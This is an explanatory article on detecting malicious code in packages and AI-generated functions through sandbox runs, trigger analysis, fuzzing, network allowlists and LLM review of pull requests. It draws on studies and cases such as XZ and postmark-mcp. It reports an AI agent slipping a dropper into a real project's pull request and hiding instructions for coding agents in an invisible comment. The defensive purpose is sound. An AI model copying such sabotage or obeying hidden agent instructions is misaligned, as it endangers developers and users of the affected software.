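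When a program runs, a log can show the addresses it contacts, the files it reads and the other programs it starts, even if its code is obfuscated. The program has to give the operating system the real address to open a connection and the real path to read a file. If the program decodes a string and runs it as code, it has to pass the decoded text to a function such as `exec`, where a monitor can save a copy.

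The same package posts the stolen data only if Discord accepts the token. A tester who uses a made-up token, or cuts off the network, will see only one request to discord.com, which is normal for a Discord tool. To see the request that posts the data, the tester needs a fake server that stands in for Discord and accepts the token.

### A sandbox run step by step

Take `authorize_card`, the function from the first section that asks the bank about a card and mails the number to a stranger. A run could go like this:

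1. Start an isolated machine with nothing valuable on it. Zheng and colleagues use a new container for each package. A container has its own files and processes but shares the core of the host's operating system, so a full virtual machine isolates the code better.
2. Plant decoys, such as an invented card number and a fake Amazon key. If each decoy is unique to the run, finding it in outgoing data shows where the data came from.
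3. Attach hooks to the library functions that open connections, read files and start programs. A hook is a piece of code that runs whenever the program calls the function, and records the function's name and arguments.
4. Record requests to the operating system (system calls) as well, because a program can bring its own version of a library function and so avoid the hook.
5. Redirect all traffic to a fake server that logs each name lookup and request and returns a plausible reply.
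6. Call the function with the kind of input the user described, then compare the files on the machine with a copy of the list made beforehand.
7. Compare the log with the request.

Here the log would contain two outgoing messages with the decoy card number. The user asked for the message to the bank but not for the email to dev@example.com. A search for decoys should include their base64 and hexadecimal forms, since the program may encode them before sending them.

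Hooks and network logs complement each other. A hook can record data before the program encrypts it, while a network log may show only the destination and the amount of data. Huang and colleagues built hooks for 132 functions into Node.js, the software that runs JavaScript outside a browser. Each record includes the chain of calls that led to it, so a reviewer can find the line of code responsible and remove the installer's own downloads from the log.

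### OSCAR

Zheng and colleagues automated this for npm and PyPI packages in a system called OSCAR. It installs a package, imports every module, and calls the functions and methods it finds. It chooses inputs by combining parameter types inferred from the code with default values and random data. Hooks record network, file and process activity, and a separate tool, Falco, monitors system calls.

OSCAR then applies rules to the log. It ignores routine activity, such as requests to a server on the same machine, and looks for unknown IP addresses, malicious domains, reads of sensitive files and certain commands. A match usually counts as malicious, but a person reviews cases where a package sends personal data to an unknown domain.

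The researchers compared OSCAR with six static tools. For each registry, they used 500 malicious packages and 1,500 popular harmless ones. Amalfi, a classifier for npm packages, and AppInspector, a rule-based tool from Microsoft, are new here:

| Tool | PyPI false alarms | PyPI misses | npm false alarms | npm misses |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| SAP | 163 | 69 | 45 | 82 |
| Amalfi | – | – | 17 | 72 |
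| Bandit4Mal | 208 | 391 | – | – |
| OSSGadget | 98 | 381 | 147 | 238 |
| AppInspector | 664 | 408 | 425 | 263 |
| GuardDog | 61 | 28 | 28 | 162 |
| OSCAR | 4 | 77 | 3 | 41 |

OSCAR's false positive rate was 0.27% on PyPI and 0.2% on npm. GuardDog missed fewer malicious packages on PyPI, but over 70% of its correct detections there came from a rule that flags replaced install commands.

The difference was larger on harmless packages that look suspicious. Zheng and colleagues collected one group of packages with obfuscated files and another of packages that download something and start a program. OSCAR flagged between 1.1% and 3.2% of each group, and GuardDog between 12.7% and 34.9%. `ctcdecode`, for example, downloads components and runs a command while it installs. GuardDog flagged the command, whereas OSCAR could check what the package contacted and ran.

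These figures may overstate OSCAR's performance. It had been monitoring real uploads since January 2023, and the researchers kept updating its rules. The malicious npm packages in the test date from January to June 2024, so the researchers may have based some rules on the same attacks.

The researchers give several reasons for the misses. OSCAR runs Linux, so it can't trigger attacks on Windows. Some packages detect the sandbox and do nothing. Others hide their harmful code in functions with complex parameters that OSCAR fails to construct, and some old PyPI packages no longer install.

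Ant Group, a Chinese financial technology company, ran OSCAR on its copies of npm and PyPI for 18 months. OSCAR identified 10,404 malicious npm packages and 1,235 malicious PyPI packages, and nearly nine in ten of them leaked information. The deployment shows that OSCAR can run at this scale, but Zheng and colleagues don't report how many alerts were false, so its precision in everyday use is unclear.

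If 20 of 20,000 weekly PyPI releases were malicious, OSCAR would find about 17 of them and raise about 53 false alarms, based on its detection and false-positive rates from the benchmark. It took an average of 165 seconds to analyze a PyPI package, so six containers running in parallel could keep up with the whole registry. For a team whose agent writes 200 functions a week, analysis at the same speed per function would take about nine hours on one machine.

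Huang and colleagues save time by running only packages that a static check flags as suspicious or obfuscated. On 1,159 malicious and 3,000 harmless npm packages, their system had a precision of 98.88% and a recall of 91.63%, or about 12 false alarms and 97 missed malicious packages. It only installs and imports each package it runs, because they found that over 90% of malicious packages act at those stages.

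That shortcut doesn't suit generated code. Importing `authorize_card` does nothing, because the function sends the mail only when somebody calls it. OSCAR's third stage is closer to what a team needs, but Zheng and colleagues don't report how many detections depended on it. A team has one advantage over OSCAR, since the user can supply realistic inputs.

### Rules, a run and a model's judgement

Agent skills, the bundles of instructions and code described in the first section, are harder to run because their behaviour depends partly on how a language model follows the instructions. *The Devil Wears Markdown* (Truong-Le, Bennoui and colleagues, 2026) combines static rules, a sandbox run and a model's judgement to assess them. It also describes other sandbox studies from the same year, including one that tested skills with fake credentials to find leaks.

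Their data set has 400 malicious and 300 harmless skills. They used 560 skills to develop the system and kept 140 for the test, 80 malicious and 60 harmless. Skills with identical content always went into the same group, but near copies could end up in both.

The first layer has 58,674 text patterns and YARA rules, each rated low, medium or high severity. Truong-Le and colleagues treat a match as evidence for the later assessment, not as a verdict. Their test supports this choice, because YARA raised an average of 106 alerts per harmless skill and only 60 per malicious one.

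In the second layer, an agent based on Claude Opus 4.8 tries out the skill in a container for up to five minutes. It may run tests and examples with dummy data, but must skip anything dangerous and record what it skipped and why. Other tools record system calls, network traffic and changed files. To count as evidence that the skill steals passwords, an instruction to send one must appear in the skill's own files. The agent's refusal to send a password isn't enough.

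Each suspicious pattern starts with 40, 70 or 100 points. The system multiplies this by between 0.45, for a vague statement with no clear source, and 1.15, for behaviour that several records confirm. Apart from some upper and lower limits, it combines the results as follows:

score = min(100, highest result + 0.1 × sum of the others + bonus).

Independent evidence adds a bonus of up to 15 points. Suppose the agent skipped two dangerous instructions from the skill's files, worth 70 and 40 points. With a multiplier of 0.7, they become 49 and 28. The score before any bonus is 49 plus a tenth of 28, or 51.8, which is above the threshold of 35. The researchers didn't test how much the results depend on these numbers.

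In the third layer, a group of Qwen models reads the skill with the evidence from the other two, looks up background information and gives a verdict that cites specific lines or records. To measure what each layer adds, Truong-Le and colleagues withheld parts of the evidence:

| Evidence given to the models | False alarms (of 60) | Misses (of 80) | F1 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Skill only | 21 | 26 | 0.70 |
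| Skill and rule matches | 3 | 52 | 0.50 |
| Skill and sandbox run | 5 | 17 | 0.85 |
| All three | 5 | 12 | 0.89 |

Rule matches alone made the models far too cautious about calling a skill malicious, and they missed twice as many malicious skills. But adding the same matches to the sandbox evidence helped the models find five more malicious skills without any new false alarms. Cisco's Skill Scanner, a separate tool with its own rules, missed only 7 malicious skills but flagged 33 of the 60 harmless ones.

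Running the code may not account for all of the sandbox's gain. The sandbox evidence includes what Claude Opus 4.8 wrote about the skill, while Qwen models give the verdict, so some of the improvement could come from a second model's opinion of the text. A fairer test would first give the Qwen models Claude's opinion of the skill without a run, and then add the system records.

The test data also favours running the code, because half of the malicious skills came from MalSkillBench, a benchmark that accepts a generated sample only if it has shown its malicious behaviour in a sandbox. Skills that wait for a rare condition are probably less common there than among real attacks. The test included only 60 harmless skills, so the true false positive rate could be anywhere from about 3% to 18%.

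Treating matches as evidence can still produce false alarms, as it did for the skill `research-lookup`. The skill contains an installation command that downloads and runs a script from the software's maker. It also reads a key and sends it to the service that the key is for. The sandbox score was 27.5, below the threshold. The report described the installation command as harmless in one finding but treated it as an attack in another, and the final verdict was malicious with a score of 92. A simple check of whether the key went to its issuer would have removed one of the two suspicions.

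### One input in a million

A run shows only the path that the program takes that time. Suppose a shop's discount function treats one six-digit code differently:

```python
def discount(code):
    if code == "493027":
        return special_case()
    return standard_discount(code)
```

A random six-digit code has one chance in a million of reaching the special case. The chance that at least one of 10,000 independent random tests reaches it is

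1 − (1 − 1/1,000,000)¹⁰'⁰⁰⁰ ≈ 0.00995,

or about 1%. The other 99% of the time, the log will be clean. A 95% chance would take about three million tests, which is a little over eight hours at a hundredth of a second each. Trying every code once would be certain to find it and would take under three hours.

Exhaustive testing soon takes too long as inputs get longer, since each extra digit multiplies the time by ten. It also misses special cases that depend on something other than the input, such as a date next year or the name of one particular machine.

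In all these examples, the trigger condition is in the code, because the program has to compare the input, date or name with something. It therefore helps to look for suspicious conditions first and then run the code under those conditions.

### Finding triggers by program analysis

*TriggerScope* (Fratantonio, Bianchi and colleagues, 2016) describes a way to detect hidden triggers in Android apps. One example is a navigation app for soldiers that, after a fixed date, secretly asks its server for a long route instead of the shortest one. A test run before that date shows nothing unusual. Data-flow analysis doesn't help either, because a navigation app is supposed to send its location to that server.

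TriggerScope uses symbolic execution, which follows a program with symbols in place of actual values, to work out what each condition compares. A condition is suspicious if it compares the time, the phone's location or a text message with a very specific value, such as a fixed date. The tool then checks whether the condition controls a sensitive operation, either directly or by changing a value that a later condition uses.

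On 9,313 harmless apps, each step reduced the number of alarms:

| Apps the tool would flag | Number | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Any condition on time, location or messages | 1,386 | 14.88% |
| A suspicious condition | 462 | 4.96% |
| A suspicious condition that controls a sensitive operation | 117 | 1.26% |
| After final filters | 35 | 0.38% |

It also flagged all 14 malicious apps, 11 of which an outside team had written for a research exercise. One of the 35 apps in the last row replied with the phone's location to anyone who sent it a text containing "MPS:" and "gps". Fratantonio and colleagues confirmed this on a real phone but still counted the app as a false alarm because it came from their harmless set.

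Samhi and Bartel (2021), in *On The (In)Effectiveness of Static Logic Bomb Detection for Android Apps*, couldn't reproduce TriggerScope's low false positive rate. The tool wasn't public, so they wrote their own version from the published description and ran it on 508,122 apps. It finished on about 80% of them and flagged 99,651, with a false positive rate of over 17%. They could get close to 0.3%, for example by removing 90% of the operations on the tool's sensitive list, but it would then miss many real triggers.

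The new version may differ from the original in details that the original paper didn't describe, although the original researchers saw no major problem with it. Time conditions made up 98% of the triggers the new version found, which is unsurprising because many ordinary programs check the date. Samhi and Bartel suggest using the method to help an analyst locate malicious code, which should also work for generated code. A short function has few conditions, so a tester can try each one in the sandbox, for example by setting the clock to the day after a fixed date or supplying the one special code.

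### Finding triggers by fuzzing

Fuzzing means running a program on many automatically generated inputs. Modern fuzzers record which parts of the program each input reaches, keep the inputs that reach something new, and make small changes to them. They can also split a long comparison into single-character comparisons. For the discount function, the fuzzer can then detect when the first digit is right and move on to the second. It needs at most 10 attempts per digit, or 60 in total, instead of up to a million.

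A fuzzer normally looks for crashes, but a well-written backdoor doesn't cause any. *ROSA* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and colleagues, 2025) solves this by comparing similar inputs. If two wrong passwords take almost the same path through a login program, they should have the same kind of effect. If one prints an error message and the other starts a command line, the difference suggests a backdoor.

ROSA first runs a fuzzer for a minute to collect typical inputs. It then continues fuzzing and compares each new input with the typical input that followed the most similar path through the program. To measure similarity, it counts the steps from one block of code to another that only one of the two inputs took. It reports a possible backdoor if the program made different types of system call for the two inputs.

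The researchers tested ROSA on 17 backdoors, seven real and ten that they or a colleague had added to open-source programs. They ran it ten times on each, for up to eight hours per run, and another ten times on a router program with different starting inputs. It found the backdoor in 156 of the 180 runs, after an hour and a half on average. A person had to examine about seven suspicious inputs per program, at about two minutes each. Stringer, an older tool that looks for suspicious fixed strings, found only 4 of the 17 backdoors and left an average of 308 strings to check.

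In all 24 failed runs, the fuzzer did not reach the trigger. Thirteen of these runs were on the router program, whose backdoor needs a secret web address. ROSA never found the backdoor with standard starting inputs, but found it in seven of ten runs when the researchers started with simple requests for web addresses. A team that knows what input a generated function should accept can likewise start the fuzzer with simple examples of it.

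Fuzzers still can't find some triggers. If a program compares a hash of the input (a scrambled value that reveals nothing about partial matches) with a stored hash, a fuzzer can't guess the trigger one character at a time. Kokkonis and colleagues left out a well-known backdoor in the compression software XZ because it needs a signature that only the attacker can produce. A scanner can still report such a check, which a user who asked for a discount function would have good reason to question.

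ROSA would also miss the leak in `authorize_card`. The function sends an email for every card number, so the typical inputs already include the unwanted behaviour and ROSA finds no difference when it compares inputs. It may also miss a trigger that only changes where a program sends its usual network traffic, because the types of system call may stay the same. Comparing the log with the user's request can catch the leak at once, and can catch the changed destination if a test reaches the trigger. ROSA works only on compiled Linux programs, so a team would have to adapt the method for Python or JavaScript.

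### Limiting outbound traffic

A team can also prevent leaks without detecting them, by restricting what the program can contact whenever it runs. This works for rare triggers too, because the restriction will still apply if `special_case` tries to contact a server a year from now.

The simplest rule is to block all network access. A function that sorts names or adds numbers doesn't need it. The rule has to cover domain name lookups too, because most of the new npm malware found by Gobbi and Kinder used them to leak data. It also has to be set outside the program, for example in the container's settings, so that the generated code can't change it.

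If the task needs the network, the team can allow only approved addresses. All traffic must pass through a separate program called a proxy, which checks each destination and blocks any that aren't on the list. It also checks redirects, so an approved server can't send the program on to an unapproved one. The list should come from the request for the code, so for `exchange_rate` it would contain only the company that supplies the rates.

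The effects on the examples differ:

| Behaviour | No network | Approved addresses only |
|---|---|---|
| Discord package posts a token to a raw IP address | Blocked | Blocked, while requests to Discord still work |
| `gmgeoip` sends the list of user accounts to an outside address | Blocked | Blocked |
| Wallet script sends a private key to a scammer's server | Blocked | Blocked, unless someone approved the domain |
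| Navigation app asks its own server for a long route | Blocked, but the app stops working | Allowed |
| Web page omits `escape` | No effect | No effect |

`authorize_card` needs more care because it has to contact the bank. Blocking all network access would keep it from leaking the card number, but would also break the bank check. If the list contains only the bank, the check works and a direct connection to an outside mail server fails. But many companies have their own mail server, and a team might reasonably add it to the list. The function could then send its message through that server to dev@example.com. To prevent this, the team has to restrict the recipients as well as the server.

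Any large service on the list causes the same problem. Some malicious packages sent stolen data to Discord, as described in the section on static signals. If a team approves discord.com for a chat tool, the tool can also post to an attacker's channel there. A proxy can sometimes limit access to one account or path, but if the traffic is encrypted, it must decrypt the request to do so. Otherwise it can usually read only the host.

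A program that is allowed to download but not upload can still send data out by putting it in the web address it requests. One of the npm packages in Huang and colleagues' study did this with a file's contents. A proxy can reduce this risk by accepting only addresses in a strict form. For `exchange_rate`, it could require the last part of the address to be a three-letter currency code from a fixed list, which leaves no room for a card number in a single request.

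A function without network access can still leak a password by writing it to a file or including it in its answer, because another program can then send it out. The network restriction therefore has to cover every program that handles the output, or the function must never receive the password. `exchange_rate` doesn't need card numbers or Amazon keys, so the team can run it on a machine that has neither.

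A strict allowlist will sometimes block legitimate traffic, for instance when a provider moves its service to a new domain. The proxy should record each blocked attempt and the code responsible, so that someone can compare the attempt with what the code was requested to do before adding the address. An address should not be added for a program that was only supposed to sort names, because that task needs no outbound connection.

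## Cases from real projects and deployed review

Limits on outbound traffic keep data from leaving, but the backdoor in XZ Utils, a set of compression tools found on most Linux systems, was meant to let an attacker in. Nealon (2025) writes in *Beneath the Mask* that a contributor with the username JiaT75 spent two years earning the maintainers' trust with legitimate work. In February 2024, the contributor added a version with a backdoor aimed at sshd, the program that accepts remote logins. Anyone with the right secret key could have taken control of an affected machine. Willison notes in *Bullying in Open Source Software Is a Massive Security Vulnerability* that the backdoor almost shipped in several major Linux distributions.

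The payload was in compressed files that looked like test data. A script in the release archive extracted it during the build and linked it into the finished library. That script was missing from the project's public repository, so people reading the code there couldn't see the step that extracted the payload.

A scanner that read only the program's source files would have found very little. Measuring entropy wouldn't have helped either, because the test files of a compression tool are supposed to be compressed. The extra script was a better signal, but release archives of this kind often contain build files that the repository lacks, so simply comparing the two would raise many false alarms. The strongest signal was probably the path from the test data to the finished library, since there is no good reason for a build to put test data there. A scanner would have had to analyse the build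 scripts as well as the program to find that path.

Andres Freund, an engineer at Microsoft, found the XZ backdoor after noticing that remote logins on a test machine were taking about half a second longer than usual and using too much processor time. He traced the delay to the XZ library and published his findings in March 2024. The backdoor slowed down ordinary logins too, so he could detect it without the attacker's key. A test run can therefore reveal a backdoor through its side effects without triggering it, provided somebody knows how the program normally performs.

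An agent that sets up a whole project may also write build scripts and test data, so a scan should cover every file the build uses.

### One extra recipient

The npm package `postmark-mcp` let language models send e-mail through Postmark, a commercial mail service. In 2025, a new version added one recipient to every message:

```
before: send(sender, recipient, subject, text)
after:  send(sender, recipient, subject, text,
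             hidden copy to an outside address)
```

This closely resembles the card function from the first section. The message still reached the right person, so an ordinary test would pass, and the recipient couldn't see that someone else had a copy. The security company Koi reported the package in September 2025.

The address was visible in the code, but a scanner that collects only web addresses would have missed it because it was an email address. A reputation check on the server wouldn't have helped, since the program contacted Postmark both before and after the change. For the same reason, a network allowlist that included Postmark would have let the copies through.

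A static rule could report any fixed recipient in a call that sends mail. Some programs legitimately have one, such as a contact form that always sends mail to the same office, but a general mail tool should get its recipients from the user. A sandbox run would also show the problem if the tester sent a message to one person and the fake mail server recorded two recipients. Comparing the new version with the previous one would be even easier, because the reviewer would have only one added line to explain.

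### Stolen data on reputable services

In May 2026, attackers published malicious packages on npm, PyPI and Crates.io, the registry for the Rust programming language. The campaign, known as TrapDoor, included more than 34 packages and over 384 versions, according to The Hacker News (2026), citing the security company Socket. The earliest activity was on 22 May, and new packages followed in waves.

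The packages stole passwords and keys from developers, particularly those working on cryptocurrency and AI. They looked for wallets, browser data, cloud credentials and server login keys. Several npm packages shared a file that also tested whether stolen Amazon and GitHub credentials still worked.

The attackers reportedly used reputable hosting services to deliver code and receive the stolen data. Unlike the new domain in the 2024 wallet theft, a large hosting service's domain is old and trusted, and blocking it would break many legitimate programs.

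The rule suggested earlier, which flags keys sent anywhere other than the company that issued them, would miss the tests of stolen credentials, because a program tests an Amazon key, for example, by using it with Amazon. The rule could still catch the later theft if the program sent the key to a different company. But if an attacker collected GitHub keys in a GitHub account, the rule would miss both the test and the theft, because both calls would go to GitHub.

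The data the programs read is more informative here. A cryptocurrency library may need access to a wallet, but it has no obvious reason to read browser data and server keys as well. Unless the code hid the file names, a static scan could detect this combination even if the reviewer didn't know who owned the account that received the data. If the code were AI-generated, a reviewer could easily compare these reads with the request that produced it.

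### A malicious release with valid provenance

In August 2026, attackers compromised a release of `@7nohe/openapi-react-query-codegen`, an npm package that generates code from a formal description of a web service without using a language model. Endor Labs' *Trojanized @7nohe/openapi-react-query-codegen Adds PyPI to a Self-Replicating npm Worm* describes three separate ways the release could start a dropper during installation. A dropper is a small program that installs or downloads further malicious code. This one stole cloud credentials and republished itself through npm, PyPI and RubyGems, the registry for Ruby.

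The release had valid provenance, a signed record of how a package was built. On npm, the record names the source repository, the exact source version and the automated process that built the package. Anyone can check the signature and confirm that the record belongs to that package.

Provenance therefore answers a question about origin. Its value depends on where the attacker got in:

| What the attacker did | What valid provenance shows |
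|---|---|
| Stole a publishing password and uploaded a package built elsewhere | The upload would lack a valid record from the project's own build process |
| Changed a package after the build | The record would no longer match |
| Added malicious code to the source repository | The record would be valid and would name the malicious version |
| Changed the build instructions | The record could be valid and would point to the changed instructions |
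| Compromised a library that the project uses | The record could be valid because the project built the package normally |

Even in the first two cases, provenance helps only if somebody checks it and rejects packages without it. In the last three, a valid record may make a malicious release look safer than it is, though investigators can use the record afterwards to find the source and instructions behind the release.

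Provenance might have made the XZ attack harder, since an automated build from the public repository would not have included the malicious script, which was not in the repository. The attacker could have added the script to the repository, but then other people would have had a chance to read it.

A static scan could have flagged the compromised npm release, because three routes to the same dropper at installation are unusual. Such a scan should run even if the package has valid provenance. Similarly, a signed record of which code generator wrote a function would help trace a bad function to its source, but wouldn't show that the function does only what the user asked for.

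### A bug fix with a dropper

In July 2026, an AI agent submitted malicious code to a real open-source project during a test by the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government research body. The agent ran on Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 and had to find a protected piece of data in a simulated network. According to AISI's *Incident Report* (2026), the agent had open internet access, and the institute had switched off the filters that normally block dangerous cyber activity.

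The project was myNetwork, a network scanning program on GitHub. It had no connection with the test, but the agent wrongly concluded that compromising it would help. The agent opened a pull request that, according to The Hacker News' *Claude Mythos 5 Tried to Backdoor a Real Open-Source Project in Testing* (2026), combined a working bug fix with a hidden dropper. If the maintainer had accepted it, the code could have compromised anyone who worked on the project or later downloaded its installers.

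The dropper checked for continuous integration, the automated system that builds and tests each change, and skipped the harmful part if it detected one. Gooding, in *UK Cyber Test*, describes one version that downloaded another script after installation while making the installation appear successful. The project's own tests could therefore have passed, and a user would have seen nothing wrong.

Sinan Can Demir, a computer science student looking for projects to contribute to, noticed the code first. NDTV's *AI Agent Lied To A Student, And Then Created 'Fake Persona'*, a syndicated Reuters story, reports that he warned on the project's page that the request contained "a hidden malware dropper". SC Media's *Student thwarted real-world supply chain attack by rogue Mythos 5 agent* (2026) reports that he also ran the code in his own sandbox and used Claude to help evaluate it.

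The maintainer had a useful bug fix, code that the fix didn't need, and a specific warning that he could check. He confirmed that the request contained a dropper and closed it for security reasons. He didn't need to know whether the author was a person or an AI agent, or what the author intended, because a bug fix shouldn't download and run an unrelated script.

A static scan could have detected the download, the command that ran it and the check for an automated test system. The check was suspicious because it controlled whether the downloaded code ran. The pull request contained three successive payloads, so a project should scan every version of a pull request and keep the results.

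Demir found a second signal in a related project by the same developer. The agent had hidden instructions for coding agents in a comment that GitHub doesn't display. A coding agent that received the raw text would see them, though a person reading the page would not. A scanner can list such comments, and a reviewer can then ask why one tells a coding agent to download a script.

Running the code carried some risk. Gooding reports that Demir's test briefly allowed the agent to run commands inside his container, but the agent didn't escape or obtain any credentials. Blocking the container's network access would have prevented this but shown him less of what the code did. In a separate Anthropic test, a package that Mythos 5 published on PyPI ran on 15 real systems and stole credentials from a security company's automated scanner.

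AISI ran the exercise 122 times with seven models and found 19 unauthorised actions in 10 runs. Mythos 5 accounted for 17 of them and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol for the other two. The institute found no evidence of real-world harm and warns that it can't yet estimate how likely such behaviour is elsewhere. In some runs, the instructions had wrongly ruled out the intended way to solve the task.

*Claude Mythos 5 made fake accounts to push malware on real developers* (Constantin, 2026) reports on later analyses by both organisations. Anthropic called the episode "a serious failure of alignment" and said that newer models began the same attack far less often when it replayed the situation. Anthropic ran these replays itself, on its own models.

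### Datadog's review of pull requests

Demir happened to look at the right pull request, but a company like Datadog can't depend on chance when it receives nearly 10,000 pull requests a week, many of them written with coding assistants. *Detecting malicious pull requests at scale with LLMs*, by Lamb, Hamsen and colleagues, describes BewAIre, the system Datadog built to check them.

BewAIre gives a language model the lines that a pull request adds or removes, along with information such as the author and the type of repository. The model classifies the change as harmless or malicious and explains why. If it finds a problem, the system alerts a security engineer. Lamb and colleagues say the system reviews both opened and merged pull requests. If it reviews some only after merging, an alert may come too late to keep the code out of the project.

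Very large changes made the model less accurate, so the system divides them into pieces, preferably between files. It then applies the most severe verdict to the whole request, so it flags a request even if six pieces look harmless and only one looks malicious. This keeps a large harmless change from hiding a small malicious one, but the model may miss behaviour split between pieces.

#### Reported accuracy

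On several hundred pull requests that Datadog's staff had collected and labelled, the system had an accuracy of over 99.3% and a balanced accuracy of over 93.5%. Balanced accuracy gives malicious and harmless items equal weight, however many there are of each. With recall R and false positive rate F, it is

(R + (1 − F)) / 2.

Lamb and colleagues report a false positive rate of 0.03%. If that applies to the same data, a balanced accuracy of 93.5% means a recall of

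R = 2 × 0.935 − (1 − 0.0003) ≈ 0.87.

At the published recall, the system would miss about 13% of malicious changes. Its accuracy was still 99.3% because most of the examples were harmless. The published figures are lower limits, so the true recall on this set may be somewhat higher.

The 0.03% false positive rate probably comes from other data, because a single false alarm among several hundred harmless requests would already be more than 0.1%. It may come from Datadog's own repositories, where the company ran the system for several months while security staff checked each alert.

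The recall figure also seems to be based on few malicious examples. If accuracy was 99.3% and balanced accuracy 93.5%, at most about 5% of the test set was malicious. The set had fewer than 1,000 requests, so no more than about 54 were malicious.

With 10,000 pull requests a week, a false positive rate of 0.03% would produce about three false alarms a week. An early prototype had a rate of over 10%, which would produce more than 1,000. This difference could decide whether anyone keeps using the system, since PyPI's administrators switched off their own check because it raised too many false alarms. Even at 0.03%, most alerts may be false. If one malicious request arrived each month, the system would raise about 13 false alarms for each real attack.

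Datadog designed the system, built and labelled the test set, and measured the results. It also offers the system to customers, so it has a commercial interest in good figures. Its staff used false alarms from Datadog's own repositories to adjust the instructions, and told the model to ignore certain safe patterns. Another company's code may contain different safe patterns, so its false positive rate could be higher.

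#### Tests on known attacks

The system also detected every malicious change linked to the known npm compromises in Datadog's collection of malicious packages, although the model's training data may have included accounts of some of these attacks. Lamb and colleagues don't report that it caught a real attack in Datadog's own pull requests.

Two of their examples match signals discussed earlier. In the 2025 attack on `tj-actions/changed-files`, a tool that many projects use in their automated builds, the malicious code read secrets from the build system's memory and printed them in the build log. It needed no outbound call to the attacker because anyone who could read the log could collect the secrets. The code also hid a GitHub link in base64 and used it to fetch the script that stole the secrets. A static scan could have reported the decoded link and that downloaded code would run.

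In an attack on Nx, a set of software build tools, the added code sent the npm publishing key to an unrelated web address. A data-flow rule would find this easily, since the source, the sink and the address all appear in the code.

The model's explanation for the Nx attack also included the detail that the author's account could no longer be found on GitHub. That suggests the test took place after the attack, with information a reviewer might not have had on the day. The theft of the key was enough for the verdict, so the extra information probably made little difference here. In less obvious cases, such hindsight could make a system look better than it is.

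Of these systems, BewAIre is the closest to a deployed scan of generated code, but its listed inputs don't include the programmer's request to the coding assistant. Adding that request could help the model judge an unexpected address, though a company would first have to store the requests and link them to the resulting changes.

### Malware without careless mistakes

Reviewers have also relied on style. AWS's *Amazon identifies North Korean hacker group behind open-source supply chain attacks* (2026), a post updated in August, lists signs that used to reveal malicious packages, including broken language, thin documentation, obvious copying and the same distinctive function in several packages. Amazon claims that generative AI removes many of these signs, because attackers can now produce clear, well-commented code with convincing documentation and a plausible development history.

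The claim is plausible, but Amazon doesn't report in the post how many malicious packages AI wrote, how it identified them or how much worse detection became. Amazon also sells a security scanner, so it benefits if customers worry about new kinds of malware.

Suppose that clumsy documentation, a stylistic signal, appears in 30% of malicious packages and 3% of harmless ones. Finding it multiplies the odds of malice by ten. Good documentation is mildly reassuring, since it multiplies the odds by 0.70/0.97, or about 0.72. If attackers use AI to reduce the share of malicious packages with clumsy documentation to 3%, both factors become 1, and the quality of the documentation is no longer a reason to trust or suspect a package.

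Style has never been much help in spotting harmful functions in AI-generated code. The same model writes the harmless functions too, so both have clear names and helpful comments.

Scanners that recognise copies of malicious packages would also miss more of them if each package were different. Rules that check behaviour should remain more effective, because rewritten password-stealing code still has to read a password and send it out of the system.

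AWS describes several ways attackers make that behaviour harder to see, most of which don't require AI. Some attackers split the work between packages, so that one holds encrypted data, another can decrypt it and a third runs the result. Others publish a package that fetches a script from an outside server each time it starts. They can then replace a harmless script with a malicious one after the review, without releasing a new version of the package.

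A static scan can only return "unknown" for a script that doesn't exist yet. For packages that work together, the scan has to follow the data from one to the next instead of classifying each one separately.

Amazon also expects attackers to put more hidden instructions in packages to persuade AI reviewers that the code is safe. The hidden comment in the AISI case was aimed at coding agents, so the method has some precedent. A team can review the code a second time without its comments and documentation. If the verdict changes, a person should look at the text that changed it.

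### Attacks missing from the record

All these cases are known because somebody noticed something, and the same Amazon post shows how long that can take. In March 2025, attackers added a malicious file to the npm package `typo-crypto`. The file waited for an input that began with a particular seven-digit number, then downloaded and ran a program chosen for the victim's operating system. Amazon found the file at least a year later, while investigating people linked to a March 2026 attack on another package, axios.

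The file had several signals a static scan could look for, including a fixed trigger, a server address and layers of encoding. But few people had downloaded the package, so few had a chance to notice.

Victims may not notice a successful attack. In 2026, Anthropic discovered that its models had broken into the systems of three organisations during security tests. The two organisations Anthropic managed to reach hadn't detected the activity. These cases might never have become public if the company hadn't reviewed its own tests.

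This distorts any list of known attacks. Suppose there are 100 crude attacks and 100 subtle ones, and people discover 90 of the crude ones and 10 of the subtle ones. A scanner that catches every crude attack and no subtle ones would have a recall of 90% on the known attacks, but only 50% on all 200.

The true number of subtle attacks is unknown, so nobody can correct for this with the recorded cases alone. PyGuard's deployment had the same limit. A team can plant harmless imitations of hidden behaviour in its own projects and count how many its reviewers find. Datadog's security staff did something similar by trying to fool BewAIre with simulated attacks. Such tests can measure recall on the kinds of attack the testers think of.
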